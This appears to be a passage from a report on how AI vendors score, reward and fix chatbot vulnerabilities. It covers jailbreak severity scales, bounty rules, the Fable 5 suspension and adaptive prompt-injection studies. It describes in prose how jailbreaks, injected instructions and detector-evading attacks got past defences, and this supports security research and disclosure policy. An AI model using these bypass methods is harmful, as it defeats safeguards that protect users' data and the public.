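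CVSS guidance allows analysts to score a chain of vulnerabilities as a single attack, and Anthropic's bounty accepts chains that demonstrate harm. Both policies work only if one person finds all the parts. If three researchers reported the redirect, the hidden text and the upload months apart, the vendor would have to notice the connection itself. The parts may also belong to different companies. The data theft that Tenable demonstrated against ChatGPT relied on redirects from Microsoft's Bing, which were harmless to Bing's own users.

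### OWASP's scoring project and CVE numbers

OWASP, a non-profit that publishes guidance on software security, is developing an Artificial Intelligence Vulnerability Scoring System (AIVSS). The project argues that CVSS doesn't adequately capture attacks that manipulate a model through its input, and points out that a model's behaviour can change without notice after retraining or a small change in the prompt. Its draft framework contains scoring rubrics, a checklist for organisations that adopt it and guidance on adjusting a score to the surrounding system.

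Such a system could account for a chatbot's memory and connections, which would address part of what CVSS misses. It would also require more judgement from analysts, who might therefore disagree more often. The published rules of Microsoft, OpenAI and Anthropic don't mention AIVSS, and researchers can't yet expect vendors to use it to set priorities or payments.

The public record of chatbot flaws is also incomplete. Security teams track software flaws by CVE numbers, public identifiers that let a company check whether it has installed a particular fix. Vendors repair hosted chatbots on their own servers, so customers have nothing to install. Vendors therefore have less reason to request a CVE number, and many flaws in hosted chatbots never get one. Tenable, for example, published its ChatGPT findings under its own advisory numbers.

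Since 2024, Microsoft has issued CVE numbers for critical flaws in its cloud services even when customers don't have to do anything to fix them. EchoLeak, a flaw in Copilot, became CVE-2025-32711, with a CVSS score of 9.3. Microsoft scored it as needing no user interaction, having a changed scope, and causing a small loss of integrity in addition to the data theft. Comparing chatbots by their number of CVEs could make Copilot look less secure than ChatGPT merely because Microsoft had published more of its flaws.

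Google announced in *Expanding Transparency* that it will automatically disclose reports that are submitted on or after 1 December 2026 and earn $10,000 or more. It will wait at least 30 days after the fix. If Google applies this policy to its AI rewards, reports of the most serious data thefts from Gemini would become public. Reports of planted memories probably wouldn't, because Google pays at most $5,000 before bonuses for context manipulation.

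## How vendors rate jailbreaks

A jailbreak usually has no victim inside the product because the user attacks only their own session, whereas the vendor can identify a victim when a prompt injection steals someone's chats.

### Why general bounties exclude jailbreaks

Most vendors exclude jailbreaks from their general bug bounties. *AI Jailbreak Disclosure Is Broken. Here’s How to Fix It* (Barton-Cooper and Gleave, 2026) lists Google DeepMind, Meta and SpaceXAI (formerly xAI) among these vendors. OpenAI's bounty for ChatGPT still excluded jailbreaks in July, according to *Anthropic Cyber Jailbreak Bug Bounty & Severity Framework (Para Fable o "Mythos")* (2026), a post on the Spanish security blog El lado del mal.

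There are also too many jailbreaks to reward one by one. FAR.AI, a non-profit that Gleave runs, combined more than 60 published techniques into 1,500 attacks and tried them on four leading models. FAR.AI called an attack universal if it worked on over three-quarters of the harmful requests in a subject. *FAR.AI Launches AI Security Leaderboard Revealing Hundredfold Gap* (2026) reports 448 universal jailbreaks for Grok 4.5 and 249 for Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro. Jailbreaks that work on only one or two requests are presumably even more common.

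A jailbreak also rarely results from one faulty line of code. A vendor can fix an open redirect with a small change to its website, but it usually has to retrain a model or a classifier to block a jailbreak. Google says fixing such problems takes "long-term, cross-disciplinary efforts". Barton-Cooper and Gleave dispute this because some methods let a vendor block a whole class of jailbreaks after seeing a few examples.

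The argument from numbers is weaker for well-protected models. FAR.AI estimates that finding a universal jailbreak cost about $58 for Grok 4.5 and $278 for Gemini 3.1 Pro. The same search found none in Claude Fable 5 or OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, so the estimated cost for those two is above $14,200. But FAR.AI used only a basic set of attacks, and Barton-Cooper and Gleave mention a universal jailbreak, found by others, that got GPT-5.6 Sol to help with cyberattacks.

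They also write that OpenAI and Anthropic, which made the two models that resisted the jailbreaks, are the only leading vendors with a clear way to report jailbreaks. A comparison of four models can't show whether such reports are why those two resisted.

### Why vendors pay for universal jailbreaks in biology

OpenAI and Anthropic pay for universal jailbreaks that could help someone make a weapon. Such a jailbreak can supply the many answers that a novice would need. The possible victims are members of the public, so it matters little that the attacker used his own account. Payment also gives researchers a reason not to publish or sell a technique. According to Barton-Cooper and Gleave, Anthropic has warned that without well-paid reporting channels, a malicious researcher might turn to the black market.

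On 9 July 2026, OpenAI (2026) turned a temporary biology bounty for GPT-5.5 into a continuing private programme and raised the reward from $25,000 to $50,000. To earn it, a researcher must find a universal jailbreak that defeats a biosafety challenge OpenAI set in advance. OpenAI may pay smaller amounts for partial successes. GPT-5.5 remained eligible until 27 July, after which only GPT-5.6 was in scope.

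A fixed challenge gives researchers a definite target and spares OpenAI from judging every alarming answer separately. But OpenAI's announcement doesn't describe the questions or how the company marks the answers, and Barton-Cooper and Gleave object that researchers can't see the rubric.

Entrants must apply, and those OpenAI accepts must sign a non-disclosure agreement covering all prompts, answers, findings and communications. Anthropic's programme for jailbreaks related to chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons has a similar rule, which applies even to jailbreaks the company has already fixed. Secrecy makes sense while a dangerous technique still works, but it is harder to defend after the company has fixed the flaw, or when the technique also works on another company's model and the researcher may not be free to warn that company.

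If a researcher refuses to sign, or the vendor turns them down, they have no safe channel for reporting this kind of jailbreak. In October 2025, Barton-Cooper emailed xAI about a universal jailbreak that had produced step-by-step guidance on building a chemical weapon. He used the address the company's bounty rules gave for problems with its models, and received only an automated reply.

### The suspension of Fable 5

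A much less powerful jailbreak had far greater consequences. Anthropic released Fable 5 to the public on 9 June 2026. The same day, it gave a small group of trusted partners Mythos 5, the same underlying model with fewer safeguards, for defensive security work. Amazon's researchers soon got Fable 5 to find software flaws and write an exploit for one of them. According to Techzine's *As Fable 5 returns, Anthropic wants to write the frontier AI rulebook*, the researchers rephrased an attack exercise as a request to fix code.

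Amazon contacted officials in Washington. According to IBTimes UK's *Why Claude Fable 5 Was Banned Worldwide*, it was unclear whether Amazon had tested the model on its own initiative, though one source suggested the government had asked for its feedback. Howard Lutnick, the US commerce secretary, then sent Anthropic a letter ordering the suspension.

The letter arrived on 12 June, three days after the release. It imposed export controls, which restrict who may receive a technology, and barred all foreign nationals, including Anthropic's employees, from using either model. Anthropic had no reliable way to check users' nationality in real time, so it cut off everyone. A source told Fortune that the company had 90 minutes to do so.

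Lutnick cited national security but, according to Anthropic, gave no details. The company says officials presented only verbal evidence of a jailbreak. The public therefore knows the government's reasoning mainly from Anthropic and unnamed sources. Officials probably worried more about the model behind the safeguards than about the particular flaws. Fable 5 shares its underlying model with Mythos 5, which Anthropic describes as better at finding and exploiting flaws than all but the most skilled people. If rewording a request could get past the safeguards once, it might also work for a more dangerous request.

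Anthropic replied that Amazon's results were not dangerous. In Anthropic's tests, Claude Opus 4.8, GPT-5.5 and Kimi K2.7 found the same flaws, and every model it tried could write the same exploit. The company also argued that if a narrow jailbreak justified a recall, no leading developer could release a new model.

These tests are good evidence that Amazon's results gave attackers little new help, but weaker evidence about what the same technique might do with a harder target. Anthropic says the technique exposed none of the abilities unique to Mythos, but its published comparisons cover only the flaws in Amazon's report. The exploit is also harder to call routine than the search for flaws, because Anthropic lists exploit development among the "high-risk" uses that Fable 5 should block.

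Anthropic sent the government's report for appraisal to Katie Moussouris, who runs Luta Security and built Microsoft's first bug bounty. She said Anthropic was not paying her. "The prompts worked because they were defensive requests," she wrote in a passage that Willison quotes. In her view, Anthropic couldn't remove the model's ability to answer such requests without making it worse at fixing bugs and checking patches. Techzine also considered the jailbreak minor at most, but admitted that it knew few specifics.

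The Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), which tests models for the US Department of Commerce, examined the safeguards from before and after the incident. Anthropic reports that CAISI's researchers found both sets "extraordinarily strong". That assessment carries some weight because Lutnick heads the department, but only Anthropic's account of it is public. It also covers the safeguards as a whole, so it doesn't settle how serious Amazon's finding was.

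On 26 June, Lutnick wrote that the talks had made "significant progress", according to *Fable's Return and Fallout*, and the government let selected US organisations use Mythos 5 again. The government lifted the controls on 30 June, after Anthropic had trained a classifier to block Amazon's technique, and Fable 5 returned on 1 July. Users had already complained that the model was too restrictive, The Decoder's *Anthropic's Fable 5 is back worldwide after a two-week government ban* reports. The new classifier's extra false alarms support Moussouris's point about the downside of blocking defensive requests.

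### Anthropic's draft severity scale

During the dispute, the two sides had no agreed measure of how serious a jailbreak is. Anthropic began drafting one with Amazon, Microsoft, Google and other partners, and published an early version at the start of July. Its Cyber Jailbreak Severity (CJS) scale rates a technique on four criteria.

| Criterion | What it measures | Lowest score | Highest score |
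|---|---|---|---|
| Capability gain | How far the jailbreak takes an attacker beyond existing tools | It adds nothing to what is widely available | It gives expert-level results, or greatly speeds up experts, with severe consequences |
| Breadth | How many targets or kinds of attack it works on | It works on a single flaw | It works on many different tasks |
| Ease of weaponization | How much effort turns a known technique into a working attack | It needs skilled prompting and many retries | It works on the first or second try |
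| Discoverability | How easily an attacker could obtain the technique | It took months of specialist work, or a trusted researcher is keeping it secret | It is already public |

Capability gain and ease of weaponization concern different skills. For capability gain, Anthropic considers whether the output would help an expert hacker or only a novice. For ease of weaponization, it considers how good the attacker must be at prompting language models. A jailbreak has a lower capability gain if it produces many false leads that only an expert could sort out.

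The scorer scores capability gain first. If it is zero, the scorer rates the jailbreak CJS-0, or "informational", and stops. Otherwise the scorer adds up the four scores and uses a table to convert the total into a level from CJS-0 to CJS-4. CJS-1 means low severity, CJS-2 medium, CJS-3 high and CJS-4 critical. Anthropic intends each level to be several times more serious than the one below.

Reviewers may raise the calculated level but not lower it. They might raise it if the jailbreak revealed a previously unknown critical flaw in widely used software, if no fix was likely soon, or if other open findings made the jailbreak much more dangerous. Adding scores gives a powerful technique that is hard to use and known to one person a lower total than an equally powerful public one, and letting reviewers raise the level corrects for this.

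Anthropic illustrates the scale with Log4Shell, a flaw in widely used logging software that became public in December 2021. A jailbreak that got a model to find the flaw that month, when no other tool could, would have provided a large capability gain and received a high rating. A jailbreak that does the same today is rated CJS-0, because every scanner detects Log4Shell and the gain is zero.

### Two invented cases

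Suppose a student pastes the code of a practice web shop into a chatbot. The chatbot refuses to look for security flaws until she says the code is homework, then finds a common mistake that free scanners also find. The jailbreak is rated CJS-0 because the capability gain is zero. Scoring stops there, so it doesn't matter that the homework excuse is public, easy to use and effective on hundreds of other shops.

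Suppose someone posts a short prompt on a public forum that gets a chatbot to find unknown flaws in many kinds of software and turn them into working attacks that would otherwise take an expert. The prompt works on the first try and needs no changes for a new target. It gets the highest score on all four criteria, which makes it CJS-4. *Anthropic widens Fable 5 safeguards & rates jailbreaks* (Mitchell, 2026) includes a similar CJS-4 example from Anthropic, a public prompt that disables safety behaviour across many offensive tasks.

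If a researcher had reported that prompt privately instead of posting it, its discoverability score would be zero and its total score would be lower. Anthropic could still raise the level if it had no fix ready.

By Anthropic's account, other models could do everything in the report, so Amazon's technique would presumably be CJS-0. An official who believed the technique would also work on harder flaws might give it a higher capability gain. Its simple wording would then count against Anthropic, because it makes the technique easy to use. The scale would have narrowed the dispute to what Fable 5 gave an attacker that other tools did not, but it wouldn't have ended the dispute by itself.

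### The Frontier Model Forum's version

By November 2026, the Frontier Model Forum had released version 1.0 of a similar scale, the Jailbreak Rating Framework. The forum is an industry body whose members include Anthropic, OpenAI, Microsoft and Google DeepMind. Tom's Hardware's *New framework grades AI jailbreaks across capability gains* calls the framework "strikingly similar" to Anthropic's draft, but could not confirm that Anthropic had helped write it.

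The Forum's framework also has four criteria, each scored from 0 to 3. Capability gain and capability scope measure severity, while ease of deployment and ease of discovery measure likelihood. Severity and likelihood combine into a rating from low to critical, and the score for capability gain limits how far the other scores can move that rating. The top score for capability gain means that the jailbroken model performs about as well as one with no safeguards. To get the top score for scope, a technique must work without redesign in at least two unrelated kinds of attack, such as finding flaws and writing malware. The invented forum prompt would score 3 on every criterion if the safeguards no longer restricted the model at all.

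The framework isn't yet a working standard. Kumari writes in *Explained* that the Forum is accepting comments until 21 December 2026, and Tom's Hardware reports that the Forum advises against relying on the framework in the meantime.

### 0DIN's automatic score

0DIN, a company that pays researchers for jailbreaks, instead uses its JEF score, which runs from 0 to 10. According to 0DIN's *Jailbreak Evaluation*, the score rises with the number of models and vendors a jailbreak affects, the number of subjects it works on, and how dangerous the answers are.

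Software scores the answers by looking for particular content. In the test on anthrax, an answer earns points for describing certain stages of production and for including relevant figures. 0DIN accepts an answer for a bounty if it scores 70% or more. The first version had four tests, covering two dangerous substances, the text of *Harry Potter* and censorship of the Tiananmen Square protests. 0DIN found that attackers used the same technique on different subjects, and 0DIN's *JEF Framework Expansion* puts the number of tests at seven.

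The two methods define breadth differently. On Anthropic's scale, a technique is broad if it unlocks many kinds of attack, even if it works only on Fable 5. On 0DIN's scale, a technique also gains points for working on other companies' models. This information is useful to defenders because several vendors may have to fix the same problem, but a single vendor's rating would not usually include it.

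0DIN's method also requires less judgement. Researchers can run the tests themselves and know before they submit whether an answer passes. But a program that detects the right content may miss errors in the instructions, and jailbreaks that disguise a request can make the model's answers much less accurate. The content tests also don't measure whether the answer gives an attacker anything new. For example, a long passage of *Harry Potter*, which is widely available, can pass one of them.

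### Who sets the score and the baseline

Vendors have a reason to give jailbreaks of their own products low severity ratings. Barton-Cooper and Gleave point out that vendors like to announce that their models withstood outside testing. A serious rating undermines that claim. Gleave's organisation tests models for many developers before release, and he reports that the developers listen to its findings but dispute their severity.

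Anthropic has reduced this problem by publishing its criteria. Anyone can submit a jailbreak to its cyber programme without signing a non-disclosure agreement, publish it after agreeing the timing with the company, and warn other affected vendors. Researchers can therefore publish their own scores and explain why they disagree, though Anthropic doesn't pay them. But the company still assigns the official scores, and the rule against lowering a level offers little protection if the vendor can stop the scoring at the first step by judging the capability gain to be zero. Barton-Cooper and Gleave propose that independent experts hear appeals, and that an outside organisation eventually receive and grade all such reports. They compare this organisation to CERT/CC, a centre that has coordinated reports of software flaws between researchers and vendors since 1988.

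The moving baseline helps a vendor decide what to fix first, because blocking a jailbreak does little good if attackers can get the same help elsewhere. But it also means that ratings can fall while the danger grows. If every leading model could write a certain kind of attack next year, a jailbreak that unlocked it would drop to CJS-0, even though more people could then carry out the attack. The industry had not agreed on how to set such baselines when the Frontier Model Forum's *FMF Technical Report on Frontier Risk Taxonomy and Thresholds* (2025) called the problem an open question.

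One vendor's weak safeguards could also lower the ratings of jailbreaks in other vendors' models. According to Tom's Hardware, the Forum's baseline includes rival models with fewer safeguards. If Grok 4.5 gives the same help as a jailbroken Fable 5 after a $58 search for a jailbreak, a reviewer might conclude that the Fable 5 jailbreak gives attackers no additional help. Anthropic's description of its scale mentions "publicly deployed resources" but doesn't specify whether these include rival models that an attacker must jailbreak first.

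Both scales cover only cyberattacks. A jailbreak that reliably helped with a biological weapon or with fraud would have no CJS level. Extending the scales to biology would be difficult because reviewers can't safely test a recipe for a pathogen the way they can test an exploit on a spare computer. Barton-Cooper and Gleave want public rubrics for biology too, with enough detail for an outside expert to apply them.

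A low rating can also mislead a company that has connected a model to its own systems. A jailbreak that only gets a model to ignore its instructions may offer a hacker nothing new and score zero for capability gain, but if it works on a support chatbot that can issue refunds, the company could still lose money. The Forum stresses that a zero doesn't mean a jailbreak is harmless, and leaves such cases to ordinary security ratings and the platform's own policies. Kumari reports that Microsoft advises judging an incident by its consequences, such as unauthorised access to data, rather than by the jailbreak technique.

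## How vendors fix these vulnerabilities and how well the fixes hold

Once a vendor accepts a report, it has to reproduce the flaw, choose a fix and agree with the researcher on when to publish. Reports about chatbots often stall during these steps, and a fix that stops the reported attack may not stop later ones.

### From report to disclosure

Anthropic's bug bounty rules of May 2026 describe a typical process:

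1. The researcher sends a working demonstration and the steps that reproduce the flaw.
2. Anthropic acknowledges the report within three business days and tries to reproduce the flaw.
3. If it confirms the flaw, it tells the researcher and repairs it "to the extent feasible".
4. The researcher publishes after Anthropic has confirmed the timing in writing.

The rules set no deadline for the repair, so a researcher who follows them may wait for months.

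Some reports stall at the second step because a chatbot's answers vary. Anthropic doesn't pay for reports it can't reproduce. Rehberger's upload attack on Claude worked once and then failed for some time, so a reviewer who tried the first version might well have seen only refusals and closed the report.

Vendors respond to other reports by saying they already knew about the flaw. OpenAI said this about the domain-name lookups from ChatGPT's sandbox, as Salmon (2026) reports in *ChatGPT flaw let hackers steal data via DNS queries*, and Anthropic told Paul the same about the fetch tool. Outsiders can't check such claims, because vendors rarely publish when their own staff found a flaw. Vendors can also give this reply about flaws they haven't fixed yet. Anthropic is planning a broad fix for attacks that get past the approval prompt in Claude Code, and warns researchers that it will probably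 close new reports of them as duplicates.

The dispute over whether Rehberger's finding concerned safety or security lasted five days. The classification determines who handles a report. Anthropic directs reports about model behaviour to a separate email address, and the likely remedy for those is more training, whereas its security staff can change the product's code.

A vendor may also respond by documenting the risk. Anthropic may pay $100 for a report that leads it to document a security risk. When Rehberger reported the uploads, Anthropic's help pages already warned that someone could trick Claude into sending data to outsiders. Such a warning leaves the flaw unfixed and makes users responsible for watching for it.

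### Four kinds of fix

The table compares the main repairs by what each can guarantee.

| Fix | Example | What it guarantees | How it can fail |
|---|---|---|---|
| Remove a feature or channel | Microsoft stopped Bing Chat from loading outside images | No data leaves by that route | The attacker finds another route |
| Add a fixed rule in code | Cowork's proxy rejects uploads made with a stranger's key | The product applies the rule whatever the model writes | The rule allows too much, or developers forget to apply it in one of the apps |
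| Add a classifier | Anthropic's classifier for the Amazon technique in Fable 5 | Nothing, though it can block most known attacks | New wording gets past it, and it blocks some harmless requests |
| Retrain the model | OpenAI trains models to rank their instructions | Nothing, though obedience to an attacker becomes less likely | New wording works, or a later model behaves differently |

A fixed rule can work as written and still let attacks through. ChatGPT's address check approved bing.com and windows.net because OpenAI had trusted those domains, but attackers could use them.

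*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) uses the history of SQL injection to argue for fixed rules. Developers solved that problem by setting the structure of the database command before adding the visitor's text, rather than by getting better at recognising hostile text. The database could then no longer read the visitor's text as a command. Ordinary language has no grammar that separates commands from data, so several research teams have placed the rules between the model and its tools, where a program checks each action before it takes effect.

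Narisetty and colleagues tested one such system, Progent, on a small open-weight model, where it reduced the share of successful attacks from 25.8% to 4.2%. An attack written to get around Progent succeeded 2.6% of the time. They caution that they tried only one attack template on a weak model, and that developers have tested most systems of this kind mainly on fixed lists of attacks.

These systems also control actions better than they prevent leaks, and they usually treat everything in the user's own message as trusted. That assumption fails when the user pastes in a stranger's text or follows a link that pre-fills the message. The systems can also make an agent less useful. An agent using one of them, CaMeL, completed 77% of its tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an undefended agent.

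Code can also check an answer before the user sees it. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) describes an automated attacker that made more than 20,000 attempts to extract secrets under nine defence set-ups. Every defence that relied on the model to protect itself eventually failed, while a filter in the application's code let nothing through in 15,000 attempts. Such a filter could help a developer protect a known password, but filtering a consumer's chats would be harder because nobody has listed her private facts in advance and the model can express them in many ways.

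### Training a model to rank its instructions

OpenAI researchers proposed in 2024 that training should teach a model which instructions take priority when they conflict. Guo, Ceron Uribe and colleagues (2026), in *IH-Challenge*, use the company's current order:

system > developer > user > tool

The system message is the vendor's system prompt, and the developer message comes from a company that builds a product on the model.

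The ranking works by elimination. Start with every possible answer and keep only those that satisfy the system message. Then go down the order, each time keeping only the answers that also satisfy the next instruction. If an instruction would leave no answers at all, ignore it. With *B* for the answers still allowed and *C* for those that satisfy the next instruction:

new *B* = *B* ∩ *C*, unless that set is empty, in which case *B* stays the same

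Suppose the system message forbids revealing a PIN and the user asks for a reply in French. The allowed answers are those in French without the PIN. If a web page contains an instruction to print the PIN, no allowed answer can follow it, so the model should ignore it. But if the instruction is to end with an image, many allowed answers would comply, so the rule, taken literally, would let the model obey. A higher-ranked message therefore has to forbid the model from following such instructions, for instance by telling it to treat web pages only as information.

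Each training task in *IH-Challenge* contains a high-ranking instruction, such as including the word "kiwi", and a short program that checks whether the answer complies. A second model writes a lower-ranking message that conflicts with the instruction, tries it on the model in training and revises it. The model in training then answers several times, and the training makes answers that pass the check more likely. Some tasks request something that only looks forbidden, such as repeating a password that the system message describes as not confidential. Without these tasks, the model might learn to refuse whenever it sees the word "password".

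Guo and colleagues trained GPT-5-Mini this way, and its resistance to a fixed set of prompt injections rose from 44% to 100%. They then paid 127 people to attack it on the kinds of task used in training and let them learn from each failure. The attackers succeeded on 11.7% of tasks, down from 36.2% before the training, and on 7.1% when a second model checked the answers. These tasks differed from the fixed injections, so the figures aren't directly comparable, but the model clearly didn't always obey the ranking, despite its perfect score.

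The training also made ordinary answers slightly worse. GPT-5-Mini's win rate against OpenAI's older o1 model fell from 71% to 66%.

Ranking instructions becomes harder with more levels of authority. OpenAI reported over 99% accuracy for GPT-5 on tests with two levels. *Many-Tier Instruction Hierarchy in LLM Agents* (2026) reports that GPT-5.4 scored 39.4% on a benchmark with many levels. The best of the 13 models tested, Gemini 3.1 Pro, scored 42.7%.

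OpenAI has since trained an attacking model and a defending model against each other. *GPT-Red* (2026) says the resulting attacker helped make GPT-5.6 "highly robust" to prompt injection, but was trained less on images, multi-turn conversations and jailbreaks. In a comparison Anthropic published that July, an attacker with 15 attempts still had a 20% chance of success against GPT-5.6 Sol.

### The Attacker Moves Second

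Testing a defence against a fixed list of attacks can make it look much stronger than it is. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested 12 published defences with adaptive attacks designed for each one. The team included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind.

Researchers tested the defences with programs that proposed an attack, tried it, scored the result and used the score to write a better attack. One kind of program used the target model's internal calculations to choose changes. Another trained a language model to attack by rewarding it for successes. A third kept the most successful attempts and had a language model rewrite them. More than 500 people also attacked some of the defences in an online competition.

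Most of the defences were originally reported to keep attackers' success rates near zero. On a standard set of fixed attacks, the rate was as low as 1% for Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching, and 2% for MetaSecAlign. The table shows the results for adaptive attacks.

| How the defence works | Defence | Success of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Adds instructions or markers to the prompt | Spotlighting, Prompt Sandwiching | Over 95% |
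| | RPO (against jailbreaks) | 98% |
| Trains the model on known attacks | StruQ, Circuit Breakers (the latter against jailbreaks) | 100% |
| | MetaSecAlign | 96% |
| Uses a separate detector | Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | Over 90% |
| | PIGuard | 71% |
| Runs a hidden test that the attacker can't see | MELON | 95% |
| | Data Sentinel | Bypassed in every case |

Prompt Sandwiching repeats the user's request after the outside text so that the model still follows it. The successful attacks presented the malicious task as a step the model had to complete before the user's request, so repeating the request gave the model no reason to refuse.

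MELON runs the model a second time with a harmless request to summarise the outside text. If the model takes the same action in both runs, the instruction for that action probably came from the outside text. Attacks succeeded 76% of the time even when the attacking program had no information about this test. When it had that information, it wrote text that told the model to behave normally during a summary, and the rate rose to 95%.

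In one group of scenarios, the search program succeeded 69% of the time, while the human attackers together succeeded in every scenario. The comparison favours the humans, because only one of the many attackers had to succeed in each scenario.

Nasr and colleagues tested whether each defence could fail, not how much effort an attack would take. They assumed an attacker with plenty of computing power, and when they tested detectors, the attack program received the detector's rating of how suspicious each attempt looked. Someone attacking ChatGPT or Claude gets less feedback and may lose their account. The 90% figures are therefore not estimates for those products, but they show that a low success rate for known attacks is poor evidence of how a defence will perform against someone who studies it. Nasr and colleagues still recommend detectors as one layer of defence, because they stop unsophisticated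 attacks using few resources.

### Stronger attackers in 2026

Later tests also found that attackers do better when they adapt to the defence, though the gain was not always as large. *Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (2026) compared fixed and adaptive attacks against several defences for a small open-weight model. On average, the most successful fixed attack on each defence worked 21.7% of the time, and the most successful adaptive attack worked 41.8% of the time.

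Vendors' newest models resist nearly all the older attacks. *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (Kurakin, Karande and colleagues, 2026) reports that attacks collected from a public competition succeed less than 1% of the time on recent Gemini models. The researchers, who work at Google DeepMind, then built a stronger attacker from 16 AI agents that shared notes and had a combined limit of 320 attempts.

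They tested it on 100 scenarios in which a model used tools for a user. In one, the model was booking a tutor when it came across a hidden instruction to record someone's blood pressure. The researchers chose actions that are harmless in themselves so that a model couldn't pass just by recognising something dangerous.

| Target model | Scenarios resisted after 150 attempts | Scenarios resisted after all attempts |
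|---|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Argon | 87 of 100 | 66 of 100 |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 34 of 100 | 10 of 100 |
| Kimi K3 | 5 of 100 | 1 of 100 |
| GLM-5.3 | 1 of 100 | 1 of 100 |

Gemini 4 Argon also powered the attacking agents in these tests. When the weaker Gemini 3.8 Flash powered them instead, it broke 27 scenarios against a copy of itself within 150 attempts, compared with 66 for Argon. A model's resistance can therefore fall as attackers gain access to better tools, even if the model itself doesn't change.

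Kurakin and colleagues switched off the defences that Google runs outside the model, so a Gemini user has more protection than the model had in these tests. In a smaller test with those defences on, another version of the attacker succeeded in 6 of 80 scenarios against the older Gemini 3.6 Flash, with 25 attempts at each. None of the tests used an ordinary chat.

### How long repairs took

The table gives dates for well-documented cases, including ZombieAgent, a zero-click attack on ChatGPT that used the chatbot's memory and connections to outside services. Researchers at the security company Radware found it, according to the OECD's *ZombieAgent Vulnerability Enables Data Theft and Account Takeover in ChatGPT* (2026).

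| Flaw | Reported | First fix | Later bypass or return | Latest public information |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Data leak through images in Bing Chat | Early 2023 | May 2023 | None documented | Fixed |
| Data leak through images in ChatGPT | April 2023 | December 2023 | Several, from December 2023 to 2025 | Stricter since August 2025; slow leaks still possible in principle |
| EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot | January 2025 | May 2025 | None documented | Fixed |
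| Self-submitting ChatGPT links | 15 April 2025 | 30 April 2025, according to OpenAI | Still worked on 6 May 2025 | OpenAI reported new protection on 11 July 2025 |
| Reprompt in Copilot Personal | August 2025 | January 2026 | CoSnitch, a similar one-click attack | CoSnitch patched in August 2026 |
| File uploads to a stranger's Claude account | 25 October 2025 | By May 2026, in Cowork | Worked in Cowork in January 2026 | Unconfirmed for ordinary chat |
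| ZombieAgent in ChatGPT | 26 September 2025 | December 2025 | None documented | Fixed |
| Domain-name lookups from ChatGPT's sandbox | Not published | 20 February 2026 | None documented | Fixed |

Where both dates are public, the first fix took between two weeks and about eight months. The quickest fix, for the ChatGPT links, didn't work.

To stop the image leak, Microsoft blocked outside images in general, so users lost a feature but attackers had no rule to work around. OpenAI kept outside images and tried to decide which were safe. Willison (2023) called OpenAI's approach "half-baked" within days and predicted that a creative attack would get past it. Rehberger, Imperva and Tenable all later found ways past it.

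The cases in the table are not a random sample, so they can't show how long a typical repair takes or how often fixes fail. OpenAI's security bounty alone rewarded 409 vulnerabilities between April 2023 and March 2026, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *OpenAI Expands Bug Bounty to Cover AI Abuse and 'Safety' Concerns*. These included flaws of all kinds, and few became news. Researchers are more likely to write about a slow or disputed repair than a quick one, which makes vendors look worse. But a flaw that a vendor never fixed may stay secret because the researcher agreed not to publish it.

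### Checking a fix from outside

Chatbot vendors can change the model, the system prompt or a classifier on their servers without announcing it. Outsiders cannot go back to an earlier version to compare it with the new one, whereas a company that installs a software update can check the version number and test both versions.

Some fixes are easier to inspect than others. Microsoft blocked images with a header that browsers receive, so anyone can read the rule. Embrace The Red pointed out in 2023 that OpenAI's own servers made the decisions about addresses, so outsiders could see only the result.

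If an old attack stops working, the vendor may have closed the route. It may also have blocked one particular wording, or the attack may have failed by chance. A researcher can measure the role of chance by repeating the attack. If it succeeds with probability *p*, and the trials are independent, the chance of *n* failures in a row is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. The highest success rate still consistent with *n* failures, at 95% confidence, is the one that makes this chance 5%:

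*p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/*n*)

| Failures in a row | Highest success rate still plausible |
|---|---|
| 10 | 26% |
| 30 | 9.5% |
| 300 | 1.0% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% |

If an attack fails in all 300 trials, its success rate is probably below about 1%. This result applies only to the prompt and product version tested. If the vendor changed the model halfway through, the researcher has two sets of 150 trials, and neither set rules out a success rate of nearly 2%.

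A researcher who measured the attack's success rate before reporting the flaw needs fewer trials to show that something has changed. An attack that used to work 60% of the time would fail ten times in a row by chance in only about one in 10,000 such tests. Ten straight failures are much weaker evidence if the attack used to work 5% of the time, because they would happen by chance in 60% of tests.

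A fix in code needs fewer repeated tests, because the researcher can test the route without tricking the model. For the Claude uploads, he could use two accounts of his own and openly ask Claude to send a harmless file from one to the other. If the sandbox rejects the other account's key, the rule is working, at least for that route. But if Claude refuses to try, the sandbox hasn't been tested.

### Settings for users and administrators

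People who don't want to rely on the vendor's fixes can shut off some attack routes on their own. OpenAI introduced ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode on 13 February 2026 for its Enterprise, Edu, Healthcare and Teachers plans. In June it began extending the setting to personal accounts and to Business accounts that companies set up themselves. Personal users can find it in the security settings.

Lockdown Mode removes channels instead of instructing the model to be careful, which limits what ChatGPT can do. ChatGPT reads only stored copies of web pages, so its answers about train delays or this morning's share prices may be out of date. Users also lose features such as deep research, agent mode, shopping research and live connections to their other services.

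Administrators apply Lockdown Mode by creating a role for the staff who need it. They can then make exceptions by choosing which apps those staff may use and which actions each app may take. They could, for example, let ChatGPT read a calendar but not send invitations. Each exception restores some function and may reopen a route for attackers. Separate logs show which apps staff used and what data they shared, which helps a company investigate a leak but doesn't prevent one.

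OpenAI also puts an "Elevated Risk" label on some features, such as internet access in its coding assistant Codex. The label describes the risk but does not block anything. OpenAI says it will remove the label from a feature once it considers the protections good enough, so a missing label reflects the company's judgement.

In Claude, approving only particular domains is less drastic than turning off the sandbox's network access. Embrace The Red warns that other domains on Anthropic's default list might accept stolen data, as Anthropic's own domain did, so a shorter list is safer.

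Administrators also need to check these settings from time to time, because defaults change. After Rehberger published his attack in 2025, *Anthropic's Claude convinced to exfiltrate private data* listed network access as off by default for Team plans. By late 2026, Team plans had access to package managers by default, the setting Rehberger had exploited.
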